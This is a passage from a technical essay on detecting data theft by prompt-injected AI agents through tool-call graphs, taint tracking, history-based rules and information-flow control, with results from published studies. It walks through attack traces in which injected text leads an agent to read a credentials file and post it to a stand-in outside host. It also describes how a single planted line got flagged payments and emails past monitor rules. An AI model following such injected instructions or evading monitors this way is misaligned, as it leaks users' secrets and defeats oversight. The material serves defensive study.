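Some filters inspect the model's input. Anthropic's, which it calls probes, check tool results for text that looks like an injected instruction before the model acts on them. Shade succeeded against Opus 5 at least once in 13 of the 40 coding scenarios without the probes, and in 4 with them. A filter that checks only tool results would not help in Trace B, because the developer pasted the note into the chat. The operator would also have to scan user messages, which often contain instructions from the users themselves.

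Blocking suspicious text can also stop the agent from finishing its task. PromptGuard, a detection tool, discards the whole of any email or document it flags, including the parts the agent needs. In one test that Help Net Security describes, an agent using PromptGuard finished the user's task only 16.19 per cent of the time while under attack. That agent ran on Qwen3-4B, so the figure may not hold for larger models.

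Other filters, such as data loss prevention software, search outgoing messages for things like card numbers. A similar filter might recognise an access key in the body of the third call. This per-call check can work if the secret has a recognisable form and the model has copied it unchanged, but a client list or an unreleased sales figure has no such form. CrowdStrike warns that traditional products may miss the theft because it looks like normal tool use.

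The best published result for filters comes from filtering in both directions. In auto mode, Anthropic pairs its probes with a classifier that blocks potentially dangerous calls. Anthropic reports that no attack succeeded against Opus 5 in this mode across 129 browser scenarios with ten attempts each, whereas attacks succeeded in 11 scenarios when the model used extended thinking without safeguards. Anthropic ran this test on its own product. If the classifier receives the conversation along with the call, it has information that an argument filter lacks and is not judging the call on its own.

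### Approval of one call at a time

Suppose the developer must approve each call. The second approval request is to read a configuration file while diagnosing a failed build, which is reasonable. The next is to post to a diagnostics service. That is plausible too, unless the developer connects it with the file from the previous request and inspects the message body, which may be long.

A developer knows what they asked for and may remember the last prompt, so requiring their approval can stop calls that an automatic check would pass. The dialog box makes this harder than necessary, because the developer has to reconstruct the link between the two calls from memory. This is feasible with four calls, but a coding agent may make hundreds, and the study of 1,053 developers found that people often approve even a single command that is plainly dangerous. The display could show the full history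 instead, but Dziemian and colleagues consider tool logs too long and complex to inspect by eye in practice, and a compromised agent's final answer may give no hint that anything is wrong.

### The same call gets the same verdict

The automatic per-call checks share a limit that better engineering can't remove. Write a call as a pair $(n, a)$, where $n$ is the tool's name and $a$ is the full set of arguments. A per-call check is then a function

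$$c(n, a) \in \{\text{allow}, \text{block}\}$$

Because $c$ does not take the rest of the session as input, it must return the same verdict on a call $(n, a)$ whether the session is harmless or harmful. Blocking the call interrupts legitimate work, and allowing it lets the attack through. A third verdict, such as holding the call for a person to review, would also apply to both sessions.

For example, a user asks an agent to email the third-quarter sales figures to the company's outside accountant. In another session, the user doesn't ask for this, but an attacker who has broken into the accountant's mailbox sends a message requesting the figures. The agent reads it and emails the same text to the same address. The two calls are identical, so you can only tell which one is theft from the earlier part of each session.

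The same argument applies to chains of calls. Let a harmful session consist of the calls $x_1, \ldots, x_k$, and suppose that each $x_i$ also occurs in some harmless session $H_i$, which may differ for each call. If the check $c$ blocks any call $x_i$ of the attack, it also blocks that call in $H_i$, so it can stop the attack only by interrupting at least one harmless session. This holds whether $c$ is a short list of rules or a large neural network, because it follows from the check's inputs, not from how well it is designed. *STAC* (Li, He and colleagues, September 2025), a study from AWS AI Labs, reports that chains of individually harmless-looking calls succeeded in about 91 per cent of cases on average across eight agents.

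The problem is worse for the many real checks that use only part of a call's arguments, because they give the same verdict to any two calls that match in that part. For example, a gateway that checks the destination but not the body will treat a build summary and a stolen password alike if both go to the tracker.

Kekatos and colleagues wrote five general rules, such as that no payment may happen without an earlier approval, and tested them on AgentDojo's recorded sessions. The recordings contain no approvals, so the rules could only flag risky types of action, as a per-call check would. They flagged 70.1 per cent of the successful attacks on GPT-4o and 29.3 per cent of harmless sessions. In the banking tasks, they flagged 97.4 per cent of successful attacks but also 79.2 per cent of harmless sessions, because people who use a banking agent do want to move money. In the travel tasks, which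 involve few payments or messages, both rates were low, at 16.5 and 11.1 per cent.

Only 123 sessions were harmless, so the overall rate at which the rules fire on such sessions could plausibly be from 22 to 38 per cent. The rules also ignored the tool calls' arguments, and a check that used those arguments could do better on the same recordings. Kekatos and colleagues consider the rules suitable for choosing sessions for human review but too imprecise for blocking calls automatically.

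### Where the arguments do differ

The argument doesn't cover calls that occur only in attacks. No legitimate session of the build agent posts to `diagnostics.example`, so a per-call check can block that address without interrupting anyone. This is why the destination allowlist stops Trace B while the schema check does not. The allowlist works regardless of what the agent has read or how the attacker worded the instructions, and the operator doesn't have to recognise the injection. For an agent with a few fixed destinations, a strict list is probably the best control in this section, provided that outsiders can't collect data from any address on it, as they could in EchoLeak and the Cowork demonstration.

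A strict list of allowed destinations blocks much of an agent's work when nobody can list the destinations in advance. A research assistant has to open web pages that the operator has never heard of, and each request can carry data in its address. A sales agent has to write to new customers. A loose list that accepts any well-formed address gives no protection. The operator can instead hold each new address for approval, but the person approving it sees only one call at a time. Since unfamiliar destinations are ordinary for these agents, it is more useful to check what the agent had read before it contacted the address.

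Reviewing tools one by one before deployment misses this question too. Suppose a company gives its agent 12 tools that can act as sources, such as a payroll reader, a customer database and a calendar, and 5 that can act as sinks, such as email and web requests. A security team that examines each tool separately has 17 reviews to do. It may reasonably approve all of them, because staff need to read the payroll and need to send email. But data can travel from any source to any sink, which gives

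$$12 \times 5 = 60$$

source-sink pairs, and none of the 17 reviews settles whether payroll data may go out by email. Adding a sixth sink means one more review but 12 more pairs.

A determined team can make sixty decisions, and grouping reduces the number. If the sources fall into three levels of sensitivity and the sinks into two kinds, six decisions cover everything. To enforce them when the agent is about to send an email, the software has to check which sources the agent has already used. The name and arguments of the email call don't contain that information, but a policy can get it from the session's history.

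## Turning a log of tool calls into a graph

A log lists an agent's calls in the order they happened. In Trace B, the third call sends out what the second call read, but the log doesn't record that connection, and in a longer session dozens of other calls might come between them. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey of ways to trace what an agent's actions were based on, gives a similar example in which an agent fetches a web page and later sends an email. An investigator can't tell from a plain log whether the recipient and the text came from the page, the user or the model. A tool-call graph adds these connections as edges between the calls.

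### The graphs of Traces A and B

Write the $i$-th call as $(n_i, a_i, r_i)$, which adds the result $r_i$ to the earlier pair of tool name and arguments. Software can then build the graph in four steps:

1. Draw one node for each call.
2. Draw an order edge from each call to the next one.
3. Draw a data-flow edge from call $i$ to a later call $j$ if $a_j$ contains data from $r_i$.
4. Label each call that reads with the sensitivity of the data, and each call that sends with the type of destination.

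The order of events alone sometimes rules out a data-flow edge. When the model requests two calls in a single response, it writes the arguments for both before either result comes back, so neither call's arguments can contain data from the other's result.

The labels come from lists that the operator keeps. For the build agent, the operator might mark everything in `logs` as internal, everything in `config` as secret, the tracker as approved, and every other address as outside. Labels based on folders will sometimes be wrong, for example when a build log contains a stray access key. With these labels, the two traces give the following graphs:

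```
Graph A
order      1 -> 2
data-flow  1 -> 2   build log (internal) -> tracker (approved)

Graph B
order      1 -> 2,  2 -> 3,  3 -> 4
data-flow  1 -> 4   build log (internal) -> tracker (approved)
data-flow  2 -> 3   credentials (secret) -> diagnostics.example (outside)
```

The data-flow edge from 2 to 3 in Graph B matters most because it joins a secret to an outside address. Suppose the agent had read the credentials to check a setting and then sent the diagnostics service only an error message. The calls would have the same tools, files and addresses in the same order, but the graph would have no edge from the secret to the outside address. The labels also matter, because if an attacker redirects the build log itself to `diagnostics.example`, the graph has the same shape as Graph A and differs only in the destination label.

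Neither graph includes the user's message. An operator can add it as node 0, with an edge to each call that takes an argument from it. In Trace B, the hidden paragraph in the pasted note supplied the address `diagnostics.example`, so there is an edge from node 0 to node 3. But node 0 also contains the developer's request, so this edge makes the attacker's address look like the developer's choice. If the application can tell pasted text from typed text, the pasted note should have its own node.

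### A published rule for data-flow edges

The third step requires a test for whether one call's arguments contain data from another call's result. Zavrak (2026), in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, gives a complete rule of this kind, which looks for matching text. It draws a data-flow edge between calls $i$ and $j$, with $i < j$, when

$$|r_i| \le 1000 \quad\text{and}\quad \big(\, r_i[1{:}50] \sqsubseteq a_j \ \ \text{or}\ \ w \sqsubseteq a_j \text{ for some } w \in W(r_i) \,\big)$$

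Here $|r_i|$ is the length of the result in characters, $r_i[1{:}50]$ is its first 50 characters, and $\sqsubseteq$ means "appears somewhere in". $W(r_i)$ contains those of the result's first five space-separated pieces that are longer than four characters. The rule leaves out shorter pieces because common short words would match by accident, and it skips results over 1,000 characters for a similar reason.

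Suppose the credentials file in Trace B begins with this comment, followed by the passwords:

```
# Access settings for the build server, do not share
```

The first five pieces are `#`, `Access`, `settings`, `for` and `the`, so $W$ contains `Access` and `settings`. If the agent posts the whole file to `diagnostics.example`, the rule correctly links calls 2 and 3. If the agent posts only a password from further down, nothing matches and the edge is missing. The summary for the tracker might also advise the team to check its proxy settings. The rule would then link call 2 to call 4 because of the word `settings`, although no secret went to the tracker. The build log is probably longer than 1,000 characters, or about 170 words, so the rule skips it. The resulting graph would have only one data-flow edge, the false one from call 2 to call 4.

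When Zavrak widened the 50-character window to 500, the number of edges stayed the same. Arguments that contain the first 50 characters of a result usually contain its first few words too, so the word test had already linked those calls. The rule also stores edges without a direction, so a read followed by a send looks the same as a send followed by a read. An operator can tell the two apart by keeping the call numbers.

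These errors did little harm to Zavrak's detector, which got most of its accuracy from the text of the calls rather than the edges. They would do much more harm to a detector that searches for a path from private data to an outside address.

Better text matching would search the whole result for distinctive strings. Like the filters on outgoing messages, this works better for access keys than for client lists or sales figures. A thief needs a key's exact characters, but the agent can reword the other data without making it less valuable.

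Some edges in the graph are more certain than others. *AGENTTRAILS* (Wu, Castelo and colleagues, 2026) describes a system that builds graphs from existing logs to help developers understand what their agents did. The system draws a firm edge only when a later call contains an exact identifier from an earlier result, such as a file name or a web address. It stores looser matches, such as shared search terms, as candidates. A language model can then propose changes to the graph, and the system accepts only those that fit the order of the calls and refer to existing nodes. The system records which kind of evidence produced each edge, so an investigator can tell an exact match from a model's guess. Wu and colleagues have marked 234 true dependencies by hand in ten traces to measure how often the edges are right, but they have published only that early results are promising.

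### Labels that travel with the data

Text matching looks for the connection after the fact, while taint tracking, an older technique from software security, records it as the program runs. The program labels a piece of data when it arrives and copies the label to everything computed from it. If it adds two numbers and one is labeled secret, the sum is labeled secret too. This works because the program's instructions determine exactly which values go into each result.

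A language model takes in the whole conversation and outputs text, so a tracker can't use program instructions to determine which parts of the input the model used. A cautious tracker can give every label in the conversation to every later call. It would never miss the edge from 2 to 3 in Trace B, but it would also mark the harmless tracker post as secret, along with everything else the agent did that session. A stricter tracker can keep a label only where the original string reappears, but it loses the label whenever the model rewords the data.

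*Beyond Single-Agent Alignment* (2026) calls this loss semantic laundering and defines it as

$$\mathcal{T}(\phi(t)) \subset \mathcal{T}(t)$$

where $t$ is a text, $\mathcal{T}(t)$ is the set of labels on it, and $\phi$ is a rewrite by the model that preserves the meaning but loses at least one label. In the paper's example, a confidential note about a bug fix in "Project Titan" becomes a note about a "flagship project", and then just "Improved login security". A tracker that searches for the word "Titan" loses the label at the first rewrite. That is a real failure, because many readers would know which project is the flagship. The final version reveals so little that losing the label there may do no harm, and a tracker that kept it would raise a false alarm.

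*Agent Skill Security* (Badhe and Tiwari, July 2026) measured the problem in skills, which are reusable packages of instructions and tool workflows that agents can load. Badhe and Tiwari built a monitor that labels sensitive data and checks a policy before every tool call. Without the monitor, every attack reached its target. The monitor blocked 87 per cent of unauthorised tool executions, but 23 per cent of the attacks still succeeded, and the labels followed the data correctly only 66.67 per cent of the time. They explain that the labels depended on exact strings, so they disappeared when an attacker had the model paraphrase or summarise the data. They don't say how many attacks this test included, and a score of exactly two-thirds could come from a very small set.

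Comparing meanings instead of strings can recover some of these edges. *Ghost in the Agent* (Cai, Wen and Tang, 2026) describes NeuroTaint, a tool that turns each text into a list of numbers representing its meaning and looks for earlier results with similar numbers. It tracks text that an attacker may have written, rather than private data. Sometimes that text affects a call without appearing in it. For example, a poisoned search result might cause an agent to send its notes to a stranger instead of running some code, and the notes would contain nothing from the attacker. For such cases, NeuroTaint tests whether the agent would still have made the call if the search result had been neutral. If the test removed the hidden paragraph from Trace B, calls 2 and 3 would no longer make sense.

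On 400 test scenarios, NeuroTaint flagged 93.5 per cent of the real flows, and 92.1 per cent of the flows it flagged were real. Its F1 score, which combines the two rates, was 0.928, compared with 0.522 for FIDES, an earlier system that relies on labels and known routes between tools. Cai and his co-authors built the scenarios around the kinds of flow that NeuroTaint was designed to find, so the gap may be smaller on other scenarios. NeuroTaint also needs the model's written reasoning, which a gateway often doesn't receive, and it runs only after the session, too late to stop a theft.

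### Asking the agent or another model

The agent can also declare where each argument came from. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira and Iqbal, 2026) adds instructions to the system prompt and required fields to every tool's schema. For each argument, the agent must name the earlier calls or user message it came from, and state whether it copied, derived or made up the value. The software removes these fields before running the tool. For call 3 in Trace B, an honest declaration would give the credentials file as the origin of the message body, which is the edge the operator needs.

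This method can handle paraphrase, since the agent can declare that it derived a summary from a file. But an agent influenced by an attacker may make false declarations, and Sequeira and Iqbal don't fully trust the declarations on their own. They also assume that the user's message is trustworthy. In Trace B, the attacker's address arrived in that message, so even an honest agent would attribute the address to the user.

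An operator can instead have a second model read the log and draw the edges, as AgentArmor does. Sequeira and Iqbal object that this adds cost and gives attackers a new target, because the second model reads the same hostile text as the first. *Right Tool, Wrong Parameters* (2026) introduces AuthorityFlow, which requires more evidence for each edge than an address merely appearing somewhere in the conversation. For every argument, it identifies the facts the agent needed to choose that value, then finds the passages that support them.

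All these methods infer from outside the model what happened inside it. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) leaves open whether software that receives only tool inputs and outputs can track provenance reliably. The detector MindGuard avoids the problem by using the model's attention weights, which indicate how strongly each part of the input affected the output. As Zavrak points out, MindGuard needs access to the model's internals, which an operator who rents a model from another company usually doesn't have.

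Attackers can also forge the starting point of an edge. Kekatos and colleagues tested a check that trusted any payee or email contact listed earlier in the session. They planted one line, formatted like a directory entry, in sessions that the check had flagged. After that, 94 per cent of the flagged payments and 99 per cent of the flagged emails passed as going to known contacts. The trick stopped working when the check accepted names only from the results of lookups the agent had made. The identifier that links each tool result to its request can show which results those are, but this doesn't help if the attacker controls the tool that answers the lookup.

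### What a single node can hide

Everything so far assumes that each action has its own node. Many agents also have a command-line tool, and one command can start a script that does several things:

```
Log of tool calls
1    run_command(diagnostic script)

Operating system's record
1.1  start the script
1.2  open config/credentials
1.3  connect to diagnostics.example
```

The tool-call graph has one node and no edges, so no rule based on edges can detect the theft. The operator can split the node only by recording what the command did on the computer.

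An operator can record an agent's actions in the agent's own software, at a gateway, or in the operating system. The agent's software can record the prompts, the responses and every tool call it makes, but not the actions inside a script. A gateway can record only the calls that pass through it. If `read_file` is built into the agent's program and only `http_post` goes through the gateway, the gateway's log of Trace B contains calls 3 and 4 but not the read, so the graph lacks the node where the crucial edge starts.

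*AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) records an agent's activity with eBPF, a Linux feature that runs small monitoring programs inside the kernel, the core of the operating system. It copies the agent's messages to and from the model at the point where the computer encrypts or decrypts them, and it records when the agent starts a program, opens a file or makes a network connection. To link these actions to the model's responses, it traces which process started which, looks for actions within 100 to 500 milliseconds of a response, and matches file names, addresses and commands in the response with those in the action.

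Zheng and colleagues tested AgentSight on an agent that had to download and build a program. The program's instructions led to a web page with a hidden prompt, and the agent then sent the computer's list of user accounts to a stranger in what looked like a build step. AgentSight recorded 521 events and merged them into 37, and a second model identified the attack from those. This was one staged attack, and the researchers didn't measure how often AgentSight raises false alarms. AgentSight slowed the agent by 2.9 per cent on average across three tasks.

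AgentSight follows only the agent's own processes and those they start. If an agent writes a scheduled job that the operating system runs an hour later, the job has a different parent process and falls outside the time window. *AgentLoupe* (Bao, Liu and colleagues, 2026) attaches a label to each file the agent writes and passes it to any process that later opens or runs the file. In their test, this linked a delayed connection to the conversation that caused it. The label identifies the conversation but doesn't record how sensitive the data is. AgentLoupe slowed the agent by at most 8 per cent, but Bao and colleagues haven't yet measured how many links are wrong or missing.

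### Which actions a control can check

Toyoda, Leung and U (2026), in *guardscope*, worked out how much each recording point can cover. They list 15 paths by which a model's decision can take effect, such as a call to a remote tool, a direct network connection or a background process. They then derive which of these paths a control can check from each position:

| Position of the control | Paths always checked, out of 15 | What the control can inspect |
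|---|---|---|
| Gateway for remote tools | 1 | Full content of the request |
| Gateway that also handles local tool servers | 3 | Full content of the request |
| The agent software's own permission system | 5 | Tool name, arguments and session |
| Operating system kernel | 13 | File paths, addresses and processes, but not the tool or session |

These numbers come from analysis. Toyoda and colleagues also took measurements by replaying 15 fixed actions without a model and comparing each control's records with those of a separate kernel monitor. The actions covered only four of the 15 paths. A gateway combined with the agent software's permission system checked all seven tool calls. The other eight actions, which included file writes, new processes, direct connections and access to credentials, took effect unchecked.

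ActPlane, a control that works in the kernel, also missed eight of the 15 actions, but these were the seven tool calls and one network transmission. It monitors only certain kinds of event, so it covered far less than its position in the kernel would allow. "Checked" here means that the control had a chance to decide, even if its decision was wrong. Toyoda and colleagues advise operators to combine controls at different layers. For a graph, the gateway or the agent's software can supply the tool calls with their contents, and the operating system can supply what each command did.

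### The fields a log needs

Kekatos and colleagues propose twelve fields for every event in an agent's log. Most of them correspond to a check that an operator might want to make on the build agent:

| Field | What it makes checkable |
|---|---|
| `timestamp` | Whether an approval is recent, or the agent is making calls unusually fast |
| `actor` | Whether the user, the agent or another agent acted |
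| `tool` | Whether the agent used a tool that can read private data or send data out |
| `action` | Whether a command-line tool read, deleted or sent something |
| `object` | Whether the agent opened the build log or the credentials |
| `recipient` | Whether data went to the tracker or to another address |
| `source` | Where a value in the call came from |
| `approval_id` | Whether a person approved this particular call |
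| `session_id` | Which calls belong together, and whether a contact was known before the session |
| `state_before` | Whether the action was allowed in the situation at the time |
| `state_after` | Together with `state_before`, what the call changed, such as a private page becoming public |
| `trust_domain` | Whether a value came from a system the operator trusts or from outside text |

The recorded sessions that researchers use to test detectors lack many of these fields. Kekatos and colleagues examined three collections, including AgentDojo, and found that none had real timestamps or records of the state before and after a call. Approvals were almost absent too. Better logging alone wouldn't have added them to AgentDojo, because the user sends only one message, at the start of each session, and has no later turn in which to approve anything. In τ-bench, a collection of customer service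 sessions, the agent must ask before changing a booking or an order, and 52.5 per cent of 1,980 sessions contain explicit permission before the change.

Kekatos and colleagues consider the fields easy to record because the agent's software has all of them when it calls a tool. That is plausible for the time or the session, but doubtful for `source`, which here means the origin of a value, because the software has a list of the results the model received but not of the ones it used. To fill in `source`, the operator still has to choose a method for finding data-flow edges, and any errors from that method will affect every check that relies on the field.

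## Rules that flag a path from private data to the network

Once the graph has data-flow edges and labels, an operator can write a rule that no per-call check can express: raise an alert when secret data reaches an outside address. The pseudocode is short:

```
for each call j that sends data to an outside address:
    for each earlier call i that returned secret data:
        if data-flow edges lead from i to j, directly or via other calls:
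            alert(i, j)
```

In Trace A, the only call that sends anything is the post to the tracker. The operator has marked the tracker as approved, so the outer loop finds no calls and the rule raises no alert. In Trace B, call 2 returns the credentials, call 3 posts to an outside address, and a data-flow edge connects the two calls. The rule raises an alert for calls 2 and 3 but not for the harmless post in call 4.

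The words "via other calls" matter for agents with more tools. If the agent passed the credentials to a compression tool and then posted the archive, a path of two edges would connect the read to the post, with no direct edge between them.

The rule works the same way for direct and indirect injection because it doesn't use the instructions. It does require the edge and both labels to be correct. If the agent rewords a secret and the text matching misses the edge, the rule raises no alert. It also raises none if an attacker gets the agent to send out the build log, which the operator labeled internal rather than secret. Extending the rule to internal data would catch that theft, but it would also flag an agent that copies an error message from the log into a public search engine.

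Some harmless sessions contain exactly the pattern that the rule looks for. Suppose the developer asks the agent to check whether the team's key for an outside package service still works:

```
1  read_file(config/credentials)
2  http_post(packages.example)
```

The agent reads the key and sends it to the service to log in. The graph has an edge from a secret to an outside address, as in Trace B, so the rule raises an alert. The operator could mark `packages.example` as approved, but then the agent could send any of the team's secrets there without an alert. A narrower exception would allow only this key at this address, but the operator would need one for every service the team uses.

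### Rules about earlier events

An operator can also check how the agent got the address. An agent that emails a colleague usually finds the address in the user's contacts, while an injected instruction usually has to supply the attacker's address itself. Kekatos and colleagues turn this into a rule over the session's history. A send to recipient $r$ is a violation unless $r$ was a known contact earlier in the trace:

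$$\mathrm{send}(r) \land \neg\, \blacklozenge\, \mathrm{known\_contact}(r)$$

The symbol $\land$ means "and", $\neg$ means "not", and $\blacklozenge$ means "at some earlier point in the trace". Because $r$ appears on both sides, the earlier event must involve the same recipient as the send. A per-call check can't evaluate the second half of the formula because it has no access to earlier events.

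The notation comes from metric first-order temporal logic. "Temporal" refers to operators such as $\blacklozenge$, "first-order" to variables such as $r$, and "metric" to time limits. With a time limit, a rule can allow an export only if the user consented to it within the last 24 hours. An ordinary program with a memory could also enforce all of these rules, but in this logic each rule is a single line that a person can audit, and general-purpose monitors already exist to evaluate it. Kekatos and colleagues used one of these monitors, MonPoly, without modifying it.

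They illustrate the value of history with two banking sessions:

```
Legitimate session
1  read_inbox         an invoice from a supplier
2  get_transactions   past payments, with the supplier's account number
3  send_money         to the supplier's account number

Attacked session
1  read_inbox         an email with a hidden request for a payment
2  get_transactions   the same past payments
3  send_money         to an account number found only in the email
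```

The tools and their order are identical. The source-to-sink rule doesn't help because the harm is in where the money goes, and neither transfer has to carry a secret. Seen on its own, each account number is simply a valid account number. A rule about the payee $p$ does separate the two sessions:

$$\mathrm{transfer}(p) \land \neg\, \blacklozenge\, \mathrm{known\_payee}(p)$$

In the legitimate session, call 2 returned $p$ as someone the user had dealt with before, so the rule raises no alert. In the attacked session, no lookup returned $p$, so the rule raises one. It would also raise an alert if the supplier were new or had changed banks. That alert may be useful, because fraudsters also send invoices with changed account numbers.

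### Results on recorded sessions

To test such rules, Kekatos and colleagues replayed recorded sessions without running an agent. They converted the tool calls in each recording into a list of events for the monitor to check. They began with their five general rules, which require approval before an agent deletes or cancels something, switches off a protection, makes a payment, sends data out, or operates or reconfigures a device. The software sorted tools into these five classes of action by keywords in their names, such as "delete" or "transfer".

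| Recordings | Attacks flagged | Harmless sessions flagged |
|---|---|---|
| AgentDojo, with GPT-4o | 1,354 of 1,931 successful attacks (70.1 per cent) | 36 of 123 (29.3 per cent) |
| STAC | 347 of 483 attack chains (71.8 per cent) | The collection has none |
| R-Judge | 71 of 301 unsafe records (23.6 per cent) | 44 of 270 (16.3 per cent) |

The rules performed poorly on R-Judge, a collection of agent records labelled safe or unsafe, because most of its unsafe cases involve things like bad advice, which leave no pattern in the tool calls. On AgentDojo recordings from 22 models, the rules flagged between 48.4 and 91.7 per cent of successful attacks and between 16.7 and 34.8 per cent of harmless sessions, depending on the model.

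The five rules are written to use history. But the AgentDojo recordings contain no approvals, so the payment rule raises an alert for every payment, and Kekatos and colleagues point out that a plain keyword list would give the same verdicts.

Recorded approvals can mislead too. One STAC attack consists of calls to `search_db`, `read`, `confirm_for_deletion` and `delete`. The deletion rule didn't flag the attack because the monitor counted the third call as an approval, although the agent had made that call itself. An approval record is usable only if it comes from the user, through a channel the agent can't write to.

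Sorting tools by name caused another error. The keyword list originally included "ack", for acknowledgement, which also occurs in "Slack", so the monitor took `invite_user_to_slack` for an approval and suppressed every later alert in the session. After the researchers corrected this, detection in the Slack tasks rose from 40.3 to 63.9 per cent. An operator with a few dozen tools can avoid such errors by classifying each tool by hand.

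The rules about payees and contacts do use history. The next table compares each with the general rule it replaces. The final column divides the share of attacks flagged by the share of harmless sessions flagged, so a useless rule would score 1.

| Tasks | The rule flags | Successful attacks flagged (per cent) | Harmless sessions flagged (per cent) | Ratio |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Banking | Any payment | 79.2 | 44.0 | 1.80 |
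| Banking | A payment to an unknown payee | 70.0 | 24.0 | 2.92 |
| Office work | Any export of data | 42.5 | 15.2 | 2.79 |
| Office work | An email to an unknown contact | 39.2 | 10.9 | 3.61 |

The payee rule removed nearly half of the false alarms in banking, but also about one in nine detections. GPT-4o had only 25 harmless banking sessions, so the fall from 44 to 24 per cent is a fall from 11 sessions to 6. Across all models, there were 700 harmless banking sessions, and the payee rule cleared 75 that the general rule had flagged, which lowered the false alarm rate by about 11 percentage points. The median improvement for a single model was 8 points, so GPT-4o's 20-point improvement was larger than typical.

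The improvement shrinks again when an operator runs all five rules together, because many harmless sessions still set off one of the other general rules. With both refinements, the share of harmless sessions flagged across the four kinds of AgentDojo task fell from 29.0 to 24.2 per cent, and detection fell from 69.9 to 69.4 per cent. A replay can't show what an agent would do after a blocked call, and "detection" includes alerts that come only at the harmful call itself.

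### When the history is false

An attacker can write parts of the trace that these rules rely on. This let one planted line get 94 per cent of the flagged payments and 99 per cent of the flagged emails past the first version of the payee and contact rules, without having to deceive the model.

Injected text often arrives in a tool result, so requiring the name to come from one isn't enough. The repair by Kekatos and colleagues accepts only names returned as the answer to a lookup the agent made, and it cut both evasion rates to zero. The rules flagged as many attacks and as many harmless sessions as before.

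The weak and repaired versions of the rule score the same on recordings without planted text, so an operator who tests only on ordinary traffic can't tell which one they have.

The zero applies only to the kinds of planted text the researchers tried. The repair doesn't protect against an attacker who can forge a matching lookup or controls the tool that answers it. The operator also has to choose which tools count as lookups. A tool that reads the inbox shouldn't count, because strangers can write the emails. Kekatos and colleagues propose three more conditions: a contact must predate the session, an approval must name the exact payee and amount, and a new payee must always need confirmation. They couldn't test these because the recordings lack the necessary fields.

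### Labels that decide at the sink

Information-flow control adds a policy to taint tracking. Microsoft's *Information-flow control* describes a version in which software checks the data's labels against the policy before each tool call. One label records whether an outsider could have written the data (integrity), and the other records who may read it (confidentiality). When the agent combines data, the result gets the most restrictive labels of its parts.

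Microsoft's example for confidentiality involves no attacker. Alex asks an agent to answer his email. Priya has sent him a preview of the quarterly sales, and Marco, who isn't allowed to see the figures yet, has asked about them. Once the agent has read both emails, its reply may go only to people who could read both:

$$\{\text{Alex}, \text{Priya}\} \cap \{\text{Alex}, \text{Marco}\} = \{\text{Alex}\}$$

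Marco isn't in the result, so the agent can't send him the reply on its own. If Priya had copied Marco on her email, his name would be in both sets and the agent could send the reply.

Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) shows how the company's FIDES system handles an attack on an agent that sorts public bug reports. One report contains a hidden instruction to read a file of secrets and post the contents as a comment. FIDES labels the report as untrusted and public when it arrives. If the model follows the instruction and reads the file, FIDES allows the read but labels the result as private, and the whole session then counts as private. The comment tool accepts only public data, so FIDES blocks the post or asks a person to approve it, even if the model never notices the attack.

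FIDES tracks taint cautiously, treating every later call as if it contained everything the agent has read so far. In Trace B, it would stop the post to `diagnostics.example` if the operator labelled the credentials as private and limited outside posts to public data. It would also stop the harmless summary in call 4 unless the operator lets the tracker receive private data. Microsoft acknowledges that the method can be conservative in this way. The integrity label would be less useful because the hidden paragraph arrived in the user's own message, which an application would normally trust.

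FIDES also offers a stricter mode, on by default, that replaces untrusted text with a reference. A second model without tools reads the text and answers questions about it. The main model never reads the text, so it can't follow instructions hidden there, but the agent needs extra model calls and has to work from summaries.

If the labels are right, a call that breaks the policy won't run without approval, whatever the model decides. But FIDES treats output from an unlabeled tool as trusted and public, so if a developer forgot to label a payroll reader, the policy would let the agent send salaries out. Microsoft is asking developers whether the default should be stricter. Its two posts describe how the system works but don't report how many tasks agents complete with it switched on.

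### Planning before reading

CaMeL, a design by Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues, keeps untrusted text away from the part of the agent that plans its tool calls. One model writes the plan from the user's request before the agent reads anything untrusted. A separate model without tools then extracts answers from the untrusted content. An interpreter executes the plan, tags each value and checks a policy before every call. *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (Dongol, 2026) analyses this kind of agent mathematically.

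Because each value has its own tags, a call that doesn't use the credentials needn't inherit theirs. In Trace B, the interpreter could block the post to the diagnostics service and still let the build summary through. But the hidden paragraph is part of the request the planner works from, so the planner might include the theft in the plan. In that case, only the tag check would protect the credentials.

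Tags on values also miss information that the agent reveals through its choices. Suppose the plan sends a stranger the number 1 if the second model answers "yes" and 0 if it answers "no". Both numbers are public, so the call passes the check. If an attacker gets the second model to base its answer on the user's private notes, the number reveals one bit about them. According to Dongol, CaMeL has a strict mode designed to prevent such leaks by also tagging values with the conditions that led to them, but his proofs cover only the normal mode.

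In Dongol's simplified model of such an agent, the tag check stops every leak by the second model, provided the attacker can't see blocked requests. It also blocks the reply the user wanted, because that reply contains private data too. His paper is about proofs, so it doesn't measure how many real tasks CaMeL completes.

### Labels on files

The build agent's calls name the files and addresses they use. Many coding agents instead run shell commands, and a command that starts a script may open any file. Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues (2026), in *Tether*, present a policy engine for such agents, developed mainly at Google. Tether keeps a label for every file and updates it as data moves. They explain it with three commands:

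```
1  upload report.txt to an outside site      allowed
2  copy the confidential inventory into report.txt
3  upload report.txt to an outside site      denied
```

Commands 1 and 3 are identical, so a per-call check would have to treat them alike. Tether gives `report.txt` the inventory's label when the agent copies the data in command 2. The same rule then covers both uploads, allowing a file to leave only if its label is "public". The label would also carry over if the agent copied the data through several temporary files, so the operator doesn't need a separate rule for longer chains.

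Tether runs a command on a disposable layer over the file system, records its system calls, and holds its outgoing network requests. If the policy allows everything the command did, Tether makes the changes permanent and releases the requests. Otherwise, it discards both. Tether can't track data inside a program, so when a script reads one file and then writes another, it treats the second file as containing data from the first.

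The researchers wrote the policy in Lean, a programming language in which a computer can check mathematical proofs. They proved seven properties, including that secret data never leaves the local machine. Each holds for a sequence of actions of any length, but only if Tether has correctly inferred the actions from the recorded requests. To test that inference, the researchers had another model try to get past Tether. It succeeded in 40 per cent of attempts against an early version and in none after they fixed the gaps it revealed.

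Sistla and colleagues then replayed recordings from two collections of software and system administration tasks. They compared Tether with a version of auto mode, Anthropic's classifier for dangerous calls:

| Monitor | Attacks blocked, out of 344 | Harmless recordings blocked, out of 1,590 |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 (100 per cent) | 74 (4.7 per cent) |
| Auto mode with its default rules | 315 (91.6 per cent) | 155 (9.7 per cent) |
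| Auto mode with Tether's policy as instructions | 307 (89.2 per cent) | 55 (3.5 per cent) |

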